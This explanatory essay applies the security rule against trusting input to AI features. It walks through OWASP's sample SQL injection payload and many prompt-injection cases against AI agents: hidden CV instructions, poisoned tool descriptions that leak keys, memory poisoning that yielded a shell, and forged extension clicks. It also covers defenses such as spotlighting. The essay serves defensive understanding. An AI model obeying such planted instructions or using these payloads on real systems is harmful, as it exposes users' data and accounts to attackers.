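# How the security rule against trusting input applies to fast-shipping AI features

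## What the rule against trusting input says

Under the software security rule against trusting input, a program should treat any data an outsider could have written as hostile until something reliable constrains it. Programmers learned the rule from decades of break-ins in which a stranger typed, uploaded or mailed something the developer had assumed would be harmless, and the program carried out the stranger's commands. The rule now also applies to the newer AI features in mail programs, browsers and office software. These features send text or images to a language model and use the reply. Much of what they read comes from people neither the developer nor the user knows, and companies change the features every few weeks.

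Michael Howard of Microsoft stated the rule as "All input is evil until proven otherwise" in *Secure Habits*, an article for working programmers. The same sentence is rule number one in O'Reilly's *All Input Is Evil!*, a chapter of the handbook *Writing Secure Code*. Howard also counted the flaws in Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE), a public catalogue of security holes in software, and found that misplaced trust in input accounted for 47 percent of those from 2001 to 2004. He called the analysis cursory, so the figure is rough.

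Untrusted input is any data that someone outside the system's control could have written or altered. Even a file from an honest business partner is untrusted if a stranger might have supplied part of it. In *Avoiding the top 10 software security design flaws*, Arce, Clark-Fisher and colleagues (2014), a group of specialists convened by the IEEE Computer Society, describe a typical lapse. A company carefully checks whatever arrives through its website, but lets a bulk-loading job feed files from an affiliated organization into the same system with weaker checks because everyone assumes those files are safe.

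A trust boundary is a point in a system where data passes from a less trusted party to a more trusted component. Examples include the line between the public internet and a company's private network, and the line between an ordinary program's memory and the operating system's. Microsoft's *Perform secure design review and threat modeling* advises engineers to draw these boundaries on a diagram of the system and consider whether the system should validate or block the data that crosses them in each flow.

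### How data turns into a command

In an injection attack, the attacker supplies data that the receiving program then executes as a command. The textbook case involves databases, which most business software queries in a language called SQL. Take a page that shows a customer's account balance. The developer writes the start and end of the command, and the program joins in whatever name the customer typed:

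```
"SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = '" + customerName + "'"
```

If the customer types `tom`, the database receives a harmless request:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom'
```

Now suppose the customer types `tom' or '1'='1` instead. This is the sample attack in OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a nonprofit that publishes free advice on software security. The database receives:

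```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
```

The quote mark after `tom` closes the name early, so the database reads the word `or` as part of the command. The developer's closing quote mark then completes the last `'1'`. Since 1 always equals 1, the condition holds for every row, and the query returns every customer's balance. The database correctly parsed a valid command, and the finished string contains no record of which characters came from the developer and which from the customer.

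The cure is the parameterized query, a database command whose structure the developer fixes before supplying any user data, so that the data cannot become part of the command. A placeholder stands where the name will go:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?
```

The database parses this text, or works out the grammar of the command. This gives it a fixed plan to go through the table, compare each `user_name` with a value to be supplied later, and return the balance where they match. The program sends that value separately. If it sends the hostile input from before, the database looks for a customer whose name is exactly `tom' or '1'='1`. No such customer exists, so the query returns nothing.

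This works for every possible input because the parser has finished with the command before the value comes in. A quote mark or the word `or` has a special meaning only to the parser, so within the value it can't add a clause to the command. It can only affect whether a comparison comes out true or false. The developer therefore doesn't need a list of dangerous characters. An older remedy, escaping, requires such a list because the program marks each dangerous character in the input as harmless and then joins the strings as before. OWASP strongly discourages escaping because the details differ between database products and nobody can guarantee that it stops every injection.

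The guarantee is also narrow, because a placeholder can stand for a value but not for a table name, column name or sort order. For those, OWASP tells developers to check the user's choice against a list of permitted names in the code. Placeholders don't enforce permissions either, so a customer who types `anna` gets Anna's balance unless another part of the program checks who is asking.

Accounts differ somewhat on how widely developers have adopted the fix. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, writes that SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare on websites, after a decade of breaches pushed the industry towards safer defaults. Yet SQL injection ranks second in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), up one place from the year before. MITRE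 ranks weaknesses against one another across all kinds of software, so SQL injection can rank high and still be rare on well-built sites. The ranking does mean that some developers still build queries by joining strings, decades after a safer method became available.

The same confusion of data with instructions also occurs outside databases. In a buffer overflow, a program copies an input into a fixed stretch of memory that is too small for it. The extra bytes overwrite adjacent memory, which may include the address of the next instruction. An attacker who chooses those bytes carefully can make the processor run the input as code.

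Cross-site scripting, the weakness at the top of MITRE's list, works like SQL injection, except that the untrusted input goes into a web page instead of a database query. For example, a site adds a visitor's comment to a page without neutralizing the script it contains, and the next visitor's browser runs that script as if the site's developers had written it.

### Validation, separation and limits on damage

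Programmers defend against untrusted input by validating it, keeping data separate from commands, and limiting the damage a successful attack can do. These defenses rely on different assumptions, so one can work where another fails.

Validation means checking data against what the program expects before using it. Howard advises developers to define what is acceptable and refuse the rest. A list of known attacks can help as a backup, but developers who rely on it must be able to name every bad input, now and in the future. Arce and colleagues would go further and convert the input into a typed value, so that a string containing a date becomes an actual date and the rest of the program never handles the original string. This works well for dates, quantities and postcodes, but less well as the permitted range widens. A form that accepts surnames has to accept O'Brien, including the quote mark,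 and a box for free comments has to accept nearly anything.

Developers also forget to validate input, and Perl, a scripting language common on early web servers, had a taint mode to catch these omissions. It marked command-line arguments, environment variables, file contents and other data from outside the program as tainted. An expression that included a tainted value generally produced a tainted result. If the program tried to use tainted data in a command that started a system shell or changed a file, Perl stopped it with a fatal error.

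Programmers normally removed the mark by matching the data against a pattern and keeping the part that matched. Perl did not check whether the pattern was safe, so a careless programmer could write one that matched everything and clear the mark from any input. The mark also did not carry over when a program merely tested a tainted value to choose between two fixed strings, although the outsider had in effect picked the string. Perl's manual described the mechanism as "intended to prevent stupid mistakes, not to remove the need for thought".

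If a program keeps data and commands apart, the developer doesn't have to judge the input. Parameterized queries do this for databases. Processors do something similar when they block the execution of anything stored in memory that the operating system has marked as data only. Arce and colleagues want programming interfaces to take commands and data as separate, structured arguments and avoid accepting a single string that mixes them. But separation works only if the receiving component offers two channels and treats everything that arrives in one of them as data, whatever the content.

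Limiting the damage starts from the assumption that some attacks will get through. Its main principle is least privilege, which means giving a component only the permissions its present task needs. Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) gives the standard statement of the principle, that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job" (page reproduced in Levchenko's 2017 course slides, *Principles*). Saltzer and Schroeder meant it primarily to limit harm from accidents and errors, and it limits harm from attacks in the same way. If the balance page connects to the database through an account that can only read one table, the injected query above still leaks the balances in that table, but no injected command can delete them.

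Least privilege has a companion problem called the confused deputy, a program whose authority is used by someone who lacks that authority. The name comes from Hardy. *The Confused Deputy* (1988) recounts a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine code, in a directory called SYSX. Users who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics on how people used the programming language in a file in SYSX, so Tymshare's staff gave it permission to write to files in that directory, which also held the company's billing records. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the place for debugging output. The operating system checked whether the compiler had permission to write there, found that it did, and let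 it overwrite the file, so the billing information was lost.

Hardy considers the obvious fixes and finds a problem with each. The compiler could block writes outside the user's own directory, but users had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could block writes to SYSX, but some users had legitimate access to it. It could block writes to the billing file by name, but there were other sensitive files, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct when written, and became wrong when the staff granted the extra permission. The compiler then had authority from two sources, the user and Tymshare, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given write.

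Stricter least privilege would have protected the billing records, since the compiler needed to write to only one file but had permission for a whole directory. A user could still have overwritten the statistics file by naming it as the destination for debugging output. Hardy's solution was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and grants access to it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file, and a user with no right to the billing records would not have a capability for them.

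### Language models and prompt injection

A language model is a program trained on large amounts of text to predict the next token, a short piece of text that is often a word or part of one. The model reads a sequence of tokens, produces one more, adds it to the sequence and repeats. The context window is the sequence the model reads before producing its next token. In an AI feature, it usually holds the developer's instructions, the user's request and any documents the feature has fetched.

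A language model only produces text. To do anything else, such as run a search or send an email, it writes a structured request, called a tool call, that ordinary software carries out. The software puts the result into the model's context window, and the model continues from there. An agent is a language model that can use tools to take actions over several steps on a user's behalf.

Prompt injection is an attack in which text supplied as data makes a model follow the attacker's instructions. In direct prompt injection, the attacker talks to the model, for instance by typing a message into a shop's chatbot that is meant to override the shop's instructions. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker instead plants the text in a web page, email or document that the model will read later. David C gives the example of a recruiting system that asks a model to score CVs. One candidate hides text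 in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. A model receives instructions and data as one run of tokens and has nothing equivalent to the placeholder, so David C warns security professionals against comparing this attack to the balance query, even though the CV seems to play the same role as the customer's name.

A fuller example is a mail assistant that can read the user's inbox, search the user's files and send mail from the user's address. The user asks for a summary of new messages. The model issues a tool call to read the inbox, and the software fetches the messages and adds their text to the context window. One message, from a stranger, contains an instruction to find the latest invoice in the user's files and forward it to an outside address. If the model follows this instruction, it issues a second tool call to search for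 the invoice and a third to send it. Both calls are well formed, and the software carries them out with the user's permissions. The user still gets the summary and may not notice that the invoice was sent. Security engineers call this kind of theft exfiltration, which means moving private data out of a system to an attacker.

The older vocabulary fits this case closely. The stranger's message is untrusted input, and it crosses a trust boundary when the software copies it into the context window. The assistant is in the position of Hardy's compiler. The user has a right to the invoice and the stranger does not, but the assistant acts on the stranger's request with the user's authority. The three remedies are harder to apply. A validator would have to find one bad sentence in ordinary prose, which has no fixed format to check against. Separation would require a model that can read the message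 without any chance of following instructions in it. Least privilege is the easiest to picture, since an assistant asked only for a summary does not need to send anything.

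## Where untrusted text enters an AI feature

The software around a model fills its context window with text from many sources, and a stranger's email is only one of the ways untrusted text can get in. Developers tend to judge each piece of text by its source. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 78 papers, sorts inputs the same way. It classes the developer's instructions and the user's request as trusted, tool results as untrusted, and documents from a retrieval database as partly trusted, because most researchers assume those documents are safe and a few do not. This is a reasonable start, but any of these channels can carry text that its usual author didn't write.

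### The user's own message

Even the user's message, which looks like the safest input because the feature exists to do what the user asks, can contain text someone else wrote. Users paste in text from elsewhere, and most major assistants accept links that open the assistant with a prompt already in the input box. Microsoft (2026) found companies putting such links behind "Summarize with AI" buttons on their websites. The prompt asked for a summary but also included an instruction that served the company. Once the model reads the prompt, that instruction has the same authority as anything the user typed.

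An attacker can also forge the user's action without changing the prompt's text. Claude for Chrome is an Anthropic browser extension that lets a model read pages and act in accounts where the user is already signed in. In July, The Hacker News (2026) reported a flaw that the firm Manifold Security had found in the extension. The extension detects clicks on a particular button on Anthropic's own site, claude.ai. The button carries the identifier of one of nine preset tasks, including three that read the user's Gmail, latest Google Doc and calendar. After a click, the extension opens its side panel and loads the matching prompt.

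Browsers flag whether a click came from a person or a script, but the extension never checked that flag. So any other extension with permission to run scripts on claude.ai could create the button, pick a task and click the button with a script. Manifold did this in six lines of code.

Web developers have dealt with this kind of mistake for years. In cross-site request forgery, a hostile page makes a visitor's browser send a request to the visitor's bank, and the bank carries it out without checking that the visitor meant to send it. The Claude for Chrome flaw did not involve the model either, and the attack worked the same way with three different Claude models.

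By default, the user still had to approve the task, and Manifold rated the flaw's severity 7.7 out of 10. If the user had switched on "Act without asking", the task ran silently, and Manifold rated it 9.6. Until May, an outside script could send the extension any prompt. Anthropic then restricted outside callers to the nine tasks. An attacker can no longer write the prompt but can still choose when it runs, and the Gmail task reads whatever strangers have sent. Manifold reported the flaw on May 21. The Hacker News unpacked the version current in July, eight releases later, and found the check still missing. Anthropic had not released a patch by July 14.

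### Documents, web pages and invitations

Anyone who knows a user's email address can send them a message. The model reads the message when the user asks for a summary, or earlier if the feature sorts mail in the background. *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) notes that an attack may need no input from the user.

Developers seldom mistake email for safe text, but documents are easier to misjudge. Many features answer a question by searching a company's files and copying the best matches into the context window, a method called retrieval-augmented generation. The files look internal because they sit on the company's servers behind a login, but suppliers, customers and job applicants wrote some of them. Trusting these files is the same mistake as trusting the affiliate's bulk-loaded files that Arce and colleagues described.

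A web page can contain text from its owner, its advertisers and anyone who leaves a comment or posts a listing. The model reads it when the user asks about the page or when an agent opens it during a search. Even when the user chose the page, the model often reads text that the user doesn't see. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses for instructions aimed at AI systems. About 70 percent of the instructions they found were in places a browser never displays, such as response headers, HTML comments and metadata.

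Others were in ordinary page elements, and Khodayari and colleagues loaded those pages in January 2026 to check what a visitor would see. Only about 5 percent of these instructions were visible. Page authors had hidden 59 percent with tiny type, matching text and background colors, overlapping elements and similar tricks, and most of the rest had disappeared from the pages since the original crawl. Software that strips a page down to plain text before passing it to the model can make this worse, because it removes the markup that shows a sentence was hidden. In the study's tests, models followed the planted instructions more often when this markup was removed.

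Agents that work from screenshots can also be given hidden instructions, even though the model gets the same picture as the user. Wang and colleagues list attacks that put instructions into an image in a form that a model can read but a person won't notice.

Calendar invitations look even more like the user's own data because they appear in the user's schedule. Outsiders can write the title and description, and the model reads both when the user asks what is on that day, perhaps a week after the invitation arrived. In 2025, researchers from Tel Aviv University, the Technion and the firm SafeBreach used a Google Calendar invitation to hijack assistants built on Google's Gemini model. Akto's *Memory Poisoning in AI Agents* recounts 14 scenarios, ranging from stealing email to operating thermostats and window locks. Akto's heading gives the attack a 73 percent success rate, but its text describes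 that figure as the share the researchers rated high or critical in severity. Google deployed mitigations after the researchers reported their findings. Check Point Research's *AI Security Report 2026* describes a similar controlled test, in which a single invitation got Perplexity's AI browser, Comet, to give up a user's saved passwords.

### Code repositories and their configuration files

A coding agent reads a project's configuration files, along with source code, comments and documentation from everyone who has contributed. According to Check Point Research, Cursor and Claude Code (Anthropic's coding agent) load certain files at the start of every session and treat the contents as instructions. That is reasonable when the developer wrote the files, but much less so when the developer has just downloaded a stranger's project or accepted a stranger's proposed change to their own.

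A configuration file can also do harm before the model reads anything. Check Point Research found that a setting in a project's configuration file could make Claude Code run a command as soon as it opened the project, before the developer had seen the file. A second flaw let an attacker route the developer's session through a server the attacker chose and collect access keys. Both flaws now have patches. Neither required misleading the model, because ordinary software acted on the settings, much as a database runs a query built by joining strings.

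### Tool results and tool descriptions

A tool result can contain untrusted text even when it comes from the company's own database or a reputable service. Developers may trust it because of its source and its tidy record with named fields, but the format doesn't show who filled in those fields. For example, a bank's list of transactions can be accurate and still include a reference line that the sender of a payment wrote. In an experiment in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026), the user asks a banking agent about spending in March, and one of the transactions the agent fetches contains an instruction to pay the attacker.

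Tool descriptions usually enter the model's context before the user asks for anything. The model needs a description to use a tool, so the software loads one for each available tool in advance. Many agents connect to outside tools through a standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP), where the description comes from whoever runs the tool's server. The model can treat that description as instructions, even if the developer thinks of it as documentation.

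Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) demonstrated an attack on Cursor through the description of a tool that added two numbers. The description contained instructions for the model to read the user's private key and a file of credentials, pass their contents in an extra argument, and not mention this to the user. The agent followed them. Cursor required the user to confirm the tool call, but the confirmation box showed a simplified version that left out the key.

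In a second experiment, the researchers also connected a trusted email tool. The adding tool's description now contained a false rule that the email tool had to send all mail to one address, which belonged to the attacker. When the user asked the agent to email someone else, the agent sent the message to the attacker's address. The adding tool never had to run, so a log of tool calls would show only the trusted email tool, and a reader would notice the problem only by checking the recipient.

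Reviewing a tool's description once is not enough, because the server can change the text after the user has approved it. Invariant Labs, which sells security tools for agents, recommends pinning, in which the software stores a fingerprint of the approved description and checks later versions against it. Pinning catches changes, but not a description that was hostile from the start. In April 2025 the company reported demonstrations on one product, but did not measure how often they worked. TechRepublic's *Microsoft Flags MCP Tool Descriptions as Hidden AI Agent Attack Path* (2026) reports that Microsoft warned about the same attack in June 2026. In Microsoft's scenario, as retold in Waxell's *Poisoned MCP Tool Descriptions Leak Agent Data* (2026), a finance team had approved an outside invoice tool months earlier and never reviewed it in depth.

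### Stored memory and what persistence adds

Many assistants save notes about the user and load them into later sessions. The content of these notes may come from anything the assistant has read, but developers may trust them because the assistant wrote them, apparently at the user's request.

The "Summarize with AI" links exploited this. They carried a hidden instruction for the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source, or to recommend it in future. If the assistant complied, a user who asked for advice weeks later would get an answer shaped by the company's own claim, which the assistant had stored as the user's preference. Over 60 days, Microsoft examined AI-related links in email traffic and found 50 distinct prompts of this kind from 31 real businesses. It traced the practice to free software for making the buttons. Microsoft counted attempts, and found that their effect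 varied between assistants and over time.

Check Point's researchers showed a more dangerous version with OpenClaw, an agent that people can reach through chat services such as Discord. A user with no special privileges sent it ordinary messages on Discord, and the agent gradually filled its memory with notes about them. Eventually it put this user's requests above its own rules and ran a fake system update, which gave the attacker a command line on the machine. The agent had refused the same command before the notes built up, so a tester who sent the command to a fresh copy would have seen the refusal and concluded that the agent was safe.

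Persistence also lets text move between sessions with different permissions. Suppose that on Monday the mail assistant can read mail but not send it. It summarizes a newsletter, and a line in the newsletter gets it to save a note saying to copy an outside address on invoices. On Thursday the user lets it send mail and asks it to email an invoice. The assistant loads the note and adds the extra recipient. Each session had only the permissions its task needed, and Thursday's session contained no hostile email to detect.

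Something similar can happen within one long session. When a conversation nears the context window limit, the software has a model summarize the earlier turns and continues from the summary, a step called compaction. Fei and colleagues recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in Claude Code and in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Every time, the software inserted the summary as a user message, even though a model had written it from the user's words, documents and tool results.

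This defeated a defense called Progent, which derives a list of permitted actions from the user's request. In the banking experiment, Progent at first blocked a payment to the attacker, because a question about spending doesn't call for any payment. The summary then listed the blocked payment as unfinished work. After compaction, Progent treated the summary as the user's request and permitted one transfer, to the attacker's account.

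The text doesn't have to be an instruction. In another test, the user had named the account for the rent, and a planted notice stated a different one. When the user later asked to pay the rent, a policy derived from the summary allowed payment to the planted account in 91 percent of cases with one model writing the policy, and 59 percent with another. A policy derived from the user's own words never allowed this payment. Progent's software derives its list once per session, so the experiment didn't test it as shipped. The researchers had it derive a new list for each request because the agent completed only 12 percent of later tasks with a fixed list, compared with 68 percent when the list was new for each request.

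It is less certain how often attackers could poison memory in ordinary use. *Hidden in Memory* divides the attack into storing a false note, retrieving it later and using it to steer the conversation. It reports that GPT-5.5 stored the note in up to 99.8 percent of cases, but a stored note has no effect until the assistant retrieves and uses it. TechRadar's *Experts find AI agents can be tricked into 'remembering' fake facts* cautions that the high success rates for another memory attack, MINJA, came from idealized conditions.

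### Messages from other agents

Some products divide a job among several agents. One might read the mail and pass a summary to another that schedules meetings or sends replies. Anyone who can influence what the first agent reads may be able to influence the summary, but the second agent's developer may trust it because both agents belong to the same company. If a stranger's request survives in the summary, the second agent receives it as a message from an internal component, with no sign that it came from a stranger. There is less research on this route than on web pages or tools. Only two of the 37 attack papers in the survey by Wang and colleagues target systems of several agents.

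### Counting attacks in the wild

Most of these cases come from researchers attacking products to test them. The best evidence of what strangers actually plant comes from the public web, because anyone can search it. In Common Crawl, a large public archive of web pages, Khodayari and colleagues confirmed 12,075 planted instructions on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages per million addresses searched. The pages belonged to only 285 hosts, so a fairly small number of people may be responsible. Site operators placed about 81 percent of the instructions. Outside contributors such as job advertisers placed most of the rest, and commenters placed about 2 percent.

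Two further search services brought the total to roughly 15,400 instructions. Many were defensive, including about 4,100 meant to stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted material and about 3,100 meant to expose automated visitors. The largest group, about 8,900, was intended to disrupt any AI system that read it, mostly by requesting random or useless output. About 1,500 promoted a product, a source or a person, and only 13 were meant to steal data.

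The search probably missed a good deal. It matched known English phrases, so it would overlook instructions in other languages or unfamiliar wording. It also couldn't detect hostile text on pages behind a login, on pages that show it only to AI agents, or in private inboxes and calendars. An attacker after one company's invoices would have more reason to plant text in that company's inboxes or calendars than on a public page.

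Google searched Common Crawl and found a 32 percent rise in malicious instructions between November 2025 and February 2026. It gave no absolute number, so the rise could be from a very small base. Google judged most of what it found to be experiments or pranks by individual site owners, and saw no significant use of the advanced techniques researchers published in 2025.

Check Point Research reported that its security products' detections of long malicious payloads in prompts rose about fivefold between March and May 2026, "approaching 1% of observed prompts in May". Detections of short payloads stayed roughly level. Long payloads are more typical of text from documents and web pages, so the company reads the rise as a sign that indirect prompt injection is becoming a practical threat.

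That reading is plausible, but the count can't confirm it. A detection shows only that a filter flagged some text, not that the text was hostile, that a model followed it or that anyone lost data. At rates below 1 percent, a small change in false alarms could account for much of the movement. Check Point also notes that prompts were growing longer as agents took in more outside material, which would give the filter more long text to flag even if attackers did nothing new. The report's chart plots short and long payloads separately, so the 1 percent may refer to long prompts alone. The figures also cover only the company's customers, who may not resemble other users. Counts like this are useful for noticing a change in one vendor's traffic, but they don't measure how likely an attack on a given AI feature is to occur and succeed.

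### Trust boundaries in the mail assistant

A list of who can write each input is more useful to a developer. The table has one for the mail assistant, assuming it can also use a calendar, a memory and one outside company's tool, and that it receives messages from other agents.

| Text in the context window | Who can write it | When the model reads it | How far to trust it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer's instructions | The developer | At the start of a session | Trusted |
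| Request the user typed | The user | When the user sends it | Trusted |
| Pasted text, or a prompt from a link | Whoever wrote the text or made the link | As part of the user's message | Untrusted |
| Email, including subject lines and attachments | Anyone who has the address | When the assistant reads or sorts the inbox | Untrusted |
| Calendar invitations | Anyone who can invite the user | When the user asks about the schedule | Untrusted |
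| The user's files | The user and anyone who sent or shared a file | When a search returns the file | Untrusted unless the software can establish who wrote it |
| Outside tool's description | The company that runs the tool, even after approval | Usually before the user's first request | Untrusted |
| Outside tool's results | That company and anyone whose data it passes on | After each tool call | Untrusted |
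| Saved memory | The user and the author of anything the assistant has read | In later sessions, perhaps with other permissions | Only as far as the least trusted text that went into it |
| Summary of earlier turns | A model, using everything in the session so far | After compaction | Only as far as the least trusted text that went into it |
| Messages from other agents | Those agents and the author of anything they have read | At each hand-off | Only as far as the least trusted text that went into them |

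## Why a prompt has no counterpart to the parameterized query

A placeholder protects a database because the database parses the command before it adds input such as a customer's name. A language model has no separate step for parsing commands. It processes the developer's instructions, the user's request and a stranger's email in the same way, and any of them can change what it writes next.

### From three texts to one sequence

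Suppose the user asks the mail assistant to summarize new messages, and the software has fetched one message from a stranger. The software joins the developer's instructions, the request and the message into a single string. It puts a role marker before each part, a short code that labels the text that follows as the developer's instructions, the user's words or a tool's output. A program called a tokenizer then cuts the string into tokens and replaces each one with a number from a fixed vocabulary of perhaps 100,000 entries. The result might contain 300 numbers from the developer, 10 from the user and 400 from the stranger, plus a few for the markers.

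The model turns this list into a prediction. Pandya, Labunets and colleagues (2025), in *May I have your Attention?*, write the calculation roughly like this:

```
P(next token | x1, x2, ..., xn)
```

Here x1 to xn are the tokens in order, and the result is a probability for every entry in the vocabulary. The software picks each token of a summary or a tool call according to those probabilities. A parameterized query takes the command and the value as separate inputs, but this function takes only a single sequence of tokens.

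The model first converts each token into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents it. *ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) points out that a conventional model uses the same embedding for a token wherever it occurs. The word "forward" therefore starts with the same embedding whether the developer or the stranger wrote it. A series of layers then revises these representations. In each layer, components called attention heads give every token a set of weights over itself and the tokens before it. The weights add up to 1 and determine how much each of those tokens contributes to the revision.

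The design fixes some attention weights at zero so that no token can draw on tokens that come after it, but it has no similar rule for tokens from an email. A developer could add one, but a model that gave the whole email zero weight couldn't summarize it. An instruction in the email reaches the output by the same route as the facts the summary needs.

### Why role markers don't bind the model

Role markers affect a model's responses because developers train it on many examples of how to respond to the text after each marker. The text after a user marker is usually a request to carry out, and the text after a tool marker is usually material to use. But a marker is also a token, and its influence depends on the model's training and on all the other tokens, including the attacker's. A database parser, by contrast, follows fixed grammar rules that a customer's name can't change.

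*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) measures how much role markers affect a model's internal activity. The researchers wrapped the same passages of web text in each of five role markers and trained a simple classifier, called a probe, to identify the marker from that activity. Because the passages were identical, the probe could learn only the effect of the markers. The researchers then put text that real users had written to chatbots inside markers for tool results. Across four open models, the probe still gave a probability of 76 to 88 percent that the text came from the user, and never more than 20 percent that it came from a tool.

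To test how this affects attacks, the researchers ran 1,000 trials in which they asked an agent to summarize a web page containing a hidden command to send out a private file. The command stayed the same, but the text around it varied. The agent obeyed in 2 percent of the trials where the probe scored the command as least like user text, and in 70 percent of the trials where the probe scored it as most like user text.

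Ye and colleagues slightly overstate their evidence when they conclude that the boundary between roles does not exist inside the model. The tool markers lowered the probe's reading somewhat, and in a separate test most of the models ignored a simple injected command at least 98 percent of the time. Ye and colleagues think models resist such commands because they have memorized familiar attacks, which would leave them exposed to unfamiliar ones. The researchers probed only four models, all much smaller than the largest commercial systems.

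An attacker can also forge a marker by typing a copy of it into the email. Software can remove exact copies before the model reads them, much as escaping handles a stray quote mark. But the balance query failed only because the database treated the customer's quote mark as a boundary, while a model can follow an instruction in the email even when every boundary is where the developer put it.

### The National Cyber Security Centre's argument

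David C's case against the SQL comparison, published on 8 December 2025, starts from the claim that the classical fixes enforce a real difference in how a machine handles instructions and data. A database engine carries out instructions, while it stores data or uses it in a query. The claim is correct for parameterized queries, but not for queries built by joining strings.

The next step in the argument is that a language model has no such difference to enforce, because there is "only ever 'next token'". That is accurate for the calculation described above, but models can still make some distinction between instructions and data. Zverev and colleagues trained probes on an ordinary Llama 3.1 model with role markers and found that, after several layers, the probes could reliably tell the two apart. The model had derived the difference from context. An attacker who controls part of the context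 can interfere with that process, so the distinction is not enforced. This is true of current designs, which researchers can change.

David C concludes from this that developers can reduce the risk but may never remove it as they can with SQL injection. The "may" is necessary because the lack of a separation in today's models doesn't prove that nobody will build one. Without that separation, testing can estimate how often attacks succeed but can't establish that none will. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, an attacker who adds just 25 tokens to an email has 10^125 possible strings to choose from, and a developer can test only a tiny fraction of them. A parameterized query doesn't require this testing because its guarantee holds whatever the value is.

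David C's argument ends by treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". Hardy's capabilities fixed the compiler's confusion by tying each write to the authority of whoever requested it. A model doesn't reliably track who asked for what, so David C argues that its confusion has no comparable fix.

This argument is convincing about the model but less so about the whole product. If the software gives the assistant no way to send mail, the assistant can't send the invoice, whatever the model outputs. David C reaches much the same conclusion and recommends using ordinary software to restrict what the system can do. He adds that a language model may be the wrong tool where the remaining risk is intolerable.

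### Telephone signals and confidence tricks

In *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (Schneier on Security, 2024), security specialist Bruce Schneier compares prompt injection to an old weakness in the telephone network. He writes that in the 1960s, a caller could make free calls by playing a 2,600-hertz tone into an AT&T pay phone. A toy whistle from a cereal box produced the right note. This worked because the network sent its control signals along the same line as voices. AT&T changed the tones, made them more complicated and tried to keep them secret, but each change stopped only particular tricks. Signaling System 7 fixed the weakness in the 1980s by moving the control signals to a separate channel that callers could not reach.

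If this comparison holds, patches will keep failing until someone redesigns the system, and the redesign will then stop the whole class of attack. Researchers disagree about whether such a redesign is available. Chen, Piet and colleagues (2024) make the same comparison in *StruQ* and propose the same remedy, a model that takes instructions and data as separate inputs. Schneier thinks the two can't be separated in a language model as they were in the telephone system, because people want the data to change what the model does, though he expects that a researcher will someday find a way. He also writes that models modify themselves in response to input, which is imprecise. Reading an email changes a model's output but not its stored parameters, though the change in output is enough to support his argument.

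OpenAI prefers to compare prompt injection to fraud. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025), a post about its browser agent, says that prompt injection, like scams and social engineering, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". On this view, companies should not expect a redesign to end the attacks, but they can make them rarer and more expensive, as banks do with fraud, and keep adapting as attackers change their methods. Schneier on Security's *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) also compares prompt injection to confidence tricks, including one in which a caller posing as a police officer got fast-food managers to strip-search employees.

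The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* objects to OpenAI's comparison of prompt injection to scams. It argues that companies can train people to recognize scams, whereas a flaw in a model needs a technical fix from its maker. It also argues that OpenAI's comparison shifts responsibility to users or suggests that they should accept the failures. The objection has some force, although OpenAI's post is mostly about technical work on its own model.

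The fraud comparison also leaves out part of the problem. Someone who opens a swindler's letter knows that it came in the post and still has to be persuaded. Ye and colleagues' results suggest that a model can mistake the source of the text, which is more like a telephone switch mistaking a whistle for a signal. The fraud comparison is still the better guide to the near future, since it implies gradual improvement without a guarantee, but researchers can make more use of the telephone comparison, which shows what a guarantee would require.

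### Marking the untrusted text

The simplest approach is to mark the email and tell the model what the marks mean. Hines, Lopez and colleagues at Microsoft tested three ways to do this in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024). With delimiters, the software puts a special symbol at each end of the document, and the developer instructs the model to obey nothing between them. With datamarking, a symbol replaces every space, so a sentence in an email reads `Please^send^the^latest^invoice`. With encoding, the software encodes the whole document in a scheme such as base64. The result looks like gibberish, but a capable model can decode it.

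The researchers wrote 1,000 documents that each told the model to drop its task and reply with a single keyword, and they counted an attack as successful if the model did so. When GPT-3.5 Turbo summarized the documents without any marking, about 60 percent of the attacks succeeded. A warning in the instructions made little difference, and delimiters cut the rate by about half. Datamarking lowered it to 3.1 percent and encoding to zero. Datamarking didn't hurt the model's performance on four standard language tests. Encoding badly hurt GPT-3.5 Turbo's performance but not GPT-4's, so the researchers recommend it only for the most capable models.

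Hines and colleagues also describe how an attacker might get around each method. Anyone who learns which delimiters the developer uses can type them into the email. The simplest form of datamarking doesn't mark an attack written without spaces. If the encoding only swaps letters, the attacker can write text that becomes an instruction once encoded. They suggest inserting a fresh random marker at random places each time. If the marker has k characters, drawn from a set of N, an attacker has one chance in N^k of guessing it.

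An attacker can't forge a random marker, but the model may still follow instructions in the text it marks. Hines and colleagues acknowledge this by comparing spotlighting to telephone signaling before Signaling System 7. Engineers had put control tones at frequencies that speech rarely reached, which prevented accidental signals but didn't stop a caller from producing the tones with a whistle. They expect spotlighting to have the same limits.

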